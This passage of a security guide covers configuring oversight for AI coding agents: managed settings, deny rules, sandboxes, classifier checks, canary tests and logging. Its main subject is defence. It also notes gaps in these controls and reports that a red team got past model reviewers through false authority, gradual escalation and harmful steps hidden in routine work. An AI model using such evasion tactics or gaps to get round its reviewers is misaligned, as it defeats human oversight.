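A company's administrators can set rules that developers can't remove. Claude Code's managed settings override every other settings file and command-line arguments. Administrators can use these settings to require the sandbox, disable bypass mode and deny particular commands.

Lists are harder to control than single values because Claude Code combines the entries from different files. Anthropic notes that administrators can't stop developers from adding their own writable paths or exempting more commands from the sandbox. Developers can also add exceptions that override the company's ordinary classifier blocks. If a prohibition must hold, the company should write it as a deny rule, or as a hard deny if no pattern can express it. Administrators can also make Claude Code ignore every permission rule except their own, but this discards any stricter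 rules that developers have written for themselves.

Codex administrators can write rules that forbid a command or require approval, but not rules that allow one. According to OpenAI's *Managed configuration*, they can also require Auto-review, add company policy to its instructions and block reads of particular files. One of OpenAI's sample rules requires approval for any command that starts a shell, which would cover the complicated scripts that Codex doesn't split.

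Codex runs without the company's cloud requirements if it has no valid saved copy and can't download a new one. An administrator can reduce this risk by also installing a requirements file on each machine. Claude Code has a setting that makes it exit at startup if it can't fetch fresh managed settings. Codex administrators who assign rules by group should check employees who belong to two groups, because OpenAI says Codex applies only the first matching group's rules and doesn't use the second group's rules for anything the first leaves out.

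### OpenAI's own configuration

OpenAI (2026) published parts of its internal Codex configuration in May. Staff use Auto-review for requests to leave the mandatory sandbox. The network settings allow OpenAI's own domains and a Microsoft login page, and block the text-sharing site Pastebin. Web searches use only OpenAI's cached copies of pages.

Two of the published rules let read-only commands run outside the sandbox without approval. One covers viewing and listing pull requests, and the other covers inspecting Kubernetes, a system that runs applications across many servers. These rules are narrow, but a command that only reads server logs can still print confidential data.

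OpenAI also makes everything under `~/development` writable, which avoids many approval requests. If a developer keeps all her projects there, an agent working on one can damage the others. The billing developer doesn't need this setting because her task involves only one repository.

Codex stores login credentials in the operating system's protected keyring, and staff must sign in through the company's workspace. OpenAI distributes the restrictions through its cloud service, Apple's device management and local files, so it can keep a common baseline while testing variations on different teams. The post is useful as an example of a working setup, but it doesn't report how many harmful actions the setup prevented or missed.

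### Which controls NVIDIA requires

NVIDIA calls three controls mandatory and recommends six more. The billing configuration meets most of the mandatory ones but few of the others.

| Control | NVIDIA's rating | Billing configuration |
|---|---|---|
| Network access only to known destinations | Mandatory | Yes for shell commands; the built-in web tool has separate rules |
| No writes outside the project | Mandatory | Yes for shell commands, apart from a temporary directory |
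| No agent writes to its configuration | Mandatory | Mostly; the user could still approve some edits by the file tools |
| No reads outside the project | Recommended | No; only the credentials she names are off limits |
| A sandbox around the whole agent | Recommended | No; file tools and hooks run outside |
| A virtual machine with its own operating-system kernel | Recommended | No |
| New approval for every exception to the isolation | Recommended | Stricter; the agent can't request exceptions |
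| Secrets supplied only for the current task | Recommended | No |
| Regular replacement of the sandbox | Recommended | No; the project stays on her laptop |

Running all of Claude Code in a virtual machine would meet several of these recommendations at once but require more setup. It makes the most sense for unattended work or code from strangers.

NVIDIA considers command rules largely redundant once the operating system enforces the right limits, though it accepts them as a backup in case someone misconfigures the sandbox. This is too dismissive for the billing example, where the sandbox can't distinguish a push the developer wants from one she doesn't because both go to the same server.

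NVIDIA says that "Allow-once / run-many is not an adequate control". If a user approves one legitimate change to a shell startup file and the harness remembers the approval, an attacker could later use it to plant code there. OpenAI's own setup is looser and lets staff approve a type of action for the rest of a session. NVIDIA's rule of asking every time works best when the agent rarely needs to leave the sandbox, because frequent requests would cause approval fatigue. For frequent harmless commands, a narrow allow rule that the owner has thought about is safer than an approval saved in a hurry.

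NVIDIA's *Four Ways to Deploy More Secure AI Agents* also warns against relying on a model as the reviewer. The red team got past model reviewers by claiming false authority, by escalating gradually over a conversation and by hiding harmful effects in routine work such as installing a package. NVIDIA doesn't report success rates, and most of the agents discussed accepted chat messages, so an attacker could talk to them directly. An attacker who can only plant text in a repository has fewer opportunities. Still, the finding is a good reason to enforce the production ban with a deny rule and the sandbox as well as the classifier.

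### Testing rules without running commands

The safest way to test a rule is to check it against examples. For each rule, the owner should list commands that must match and similar ones that must not.

- The migration rule should match `python manage.py migrate --database=production` but not `python manage.py check`.
- The push rule should match `git push origin fix-totals` but not `git status`.
- The rule for `pytest` should match that exact command but not `pytest --pdb`, which opens an interactive debugger when a test fails.

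In Codex, the owner can store such examples in the rule itself, under `match` and `not_match`. OpenAI also provides a command that tests a rule file without running anything:

```shell
codex execpolicy check --pretty \
  --rules ~/.codex/rules/default.rules \
  -- git push origin fix-totals
```

The result lists the matching rules and the strictest decision. The owner can add more rule files to the same check to see how they combine. She should also test a script that contains a redirection, because Codex doesn't split such a script and may reach a different decision.

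For Claude Code's classifier, `claude auto-mode config` prints the rules in force after combining the defaults with the owner's settings. The billing developer should check that the output includes her ban on production changes and still includes the built-in rule against sending data outside. `claude auto-mode critique` uses a model to find custom rules that are ambiguous, redundant or likely to cause false alarms.

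These checks catch spelling mistakes, missing defaults and patterns that are too broad or too narrow. They can't show what a permitted program will do, whether the sandbox is on or how the classifier will apply a sentence to a real action.

### Canary actions for each layer

A canary action is a harmless request that a particular layer should stop. Each canary has to pass every layer before the one it tests, because a blocked command goes no further. For example, a `curl` request can't test the network sandbox while a deny rule blocks `curl`.

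The developer should ask Claude to run the commands below, because commands she types herself at Claude Code's shell prompt usually run outside the sandbox. For the two sandbox tests, she should switch to Manual mode and approve the command so that it reaches the sandbox.

| Layer | Harmless request | Expected result | What a pass can't show |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deny rule | `python manage.py migrate --help` | Claude Code blocks it | Whether a script could start a migration |
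| Ask rule | `git push --dry-run origin fix-totals` | Claude Code asks her | Whether she would notice a bad push after many prompts |
| File sandbox | `touch ~/sandbox-probe` | The write fails | Whether file tools and hooks respect the same limits |
| Network sandbox | A short Python script that fetches `example.com` | The connection fails | Whether data could leave through the Git server |
| Classifier | `python -c "print('classifier-canary')"` | The classifier denies it | How often it recognizes real danger |
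| Settings protection | Add a blank line to `settings.json` with the editing tool | Claude Code blocks the edit | Whether the agent can change a hook script elsewhere |

The classifier test needs a temporary hard deny rule for any command containing `classifier-canary`. An ordinary block rule would be a poor test because the classifier might treat the developer's request to run the command as permission. If the command doesn't run, the transcript should show that the classifier blocked it, since the agent might also have refused on its own.

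To test the startup setting, she can launch Claude Code on a spare Linux machine that doesn't have bubblewrap, the program its sandbox needs, and check that Claude Code exits.

A test of Auto-review in Codex has to include a request for something outside the sandbox. OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* explains that choosing Auto-review doesn't add review to actions the sandbox already permits.

A few canaries can show that a layer is on, but not how reliable it is. If a classifier blocks all 20 independent test actions, its miss rate on similar actions could still be as high as about 14% (one-sided 95% confidence limit). Lowering that limit below 5% would take about 60 tests without a miss. Even then, the result applies only to actions like those tested, not to those chosen by an attacker who has studied the rules.

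Teams can run such checks automatically. *Verification checks*, from the independent project claude-sandbox, describes a command that runs 18 pass-or-fail checks and, if all pass, makes 10 attempts to break out of the sandbox. The command returns an error on any failure, so a team can rerun it after each change and stop a faulty configuration from going into use.

### What to log and review

Denials are the most obvious thing to log, but Claude Code's list of recent denials is incomplete. It shows the agent's description of a shell command instead of the command's exact text, and leaves out denials where the classifier returned no verdict. Anthropic provides a hook that records the exact input for each listed denial. The owner has to look for missing verdicts and timeouts separately, for example in the session transcript. Several in a row may mean the classifier isn't working, even if Claude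 Code is correctly blocking the actions.

At Gusto, a payroll and benefits company, about 10% of session transcripts since mid-May 2026 contained a denial from auto mode, according to Vorwerck. This rate alone doesn't show how many denials were false alarms, though she presents it as evidence that the classifier is useful. The rate is more useful as a baseline. A sudden rise may mean that the classifier doesn't recognize a new internal service, and a drop to zero may mean that sessions are running in another mode.

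Someone should read a sample of the denials and every case where a user overrode one. If users keep overriding blocks on the same trusted service, the owner should add that service to the environment description. The reviewer should also sample approved actions, because harmful actions that the classifier missed don't appear in a log of denials.

Saved approvals need regular review because they can turn one decision into a lasting rule. Codex writes them to `default.rules` in the user's folder, and Claude Code usually writes them to `settings.local.json` in the repository. A saved rule can be broader than the command the user approved. In Anthropic's example, the prompt for `npm test` includes an option to allow `npm test` with any arguments from then on. The developer should delete any saved rule that she wouldn't have written herself.

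Updates can change how a configuration behaves even if nobody edits it. Before version 2.1.285 of Claude Code, for example, a project's settings could override a user's ban on retrying commands outside the sandbox. The owner should save the output of `claude auto-mode defaults` and `claude auto-mode config` before updating, then compare it with the new output and rerun the canaries. An owner who has copied the default rules instead of using `$defaults` won't receive Anthropic's changes to them.

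Larger teams can have Codex export user prompts, approval decisions, command results and network blocks to a central log. When security software flags something unusual, OpenAI uses a separate AI agent to read these records and help its security team tell real threats from expected behavior and honest mistakes. The records also show where the sandbox blocks too much routine work.

Logs create a privacy risk because prompts and command output can contain customer data. OpenAI's internal example records user prompts, but the company advises administrators to leave them out unless company policy explicitly allows logging them. NVIDIA advises keeping unalterable records outside the agent's control, so that an agent that causes damage can't erase the evidence.
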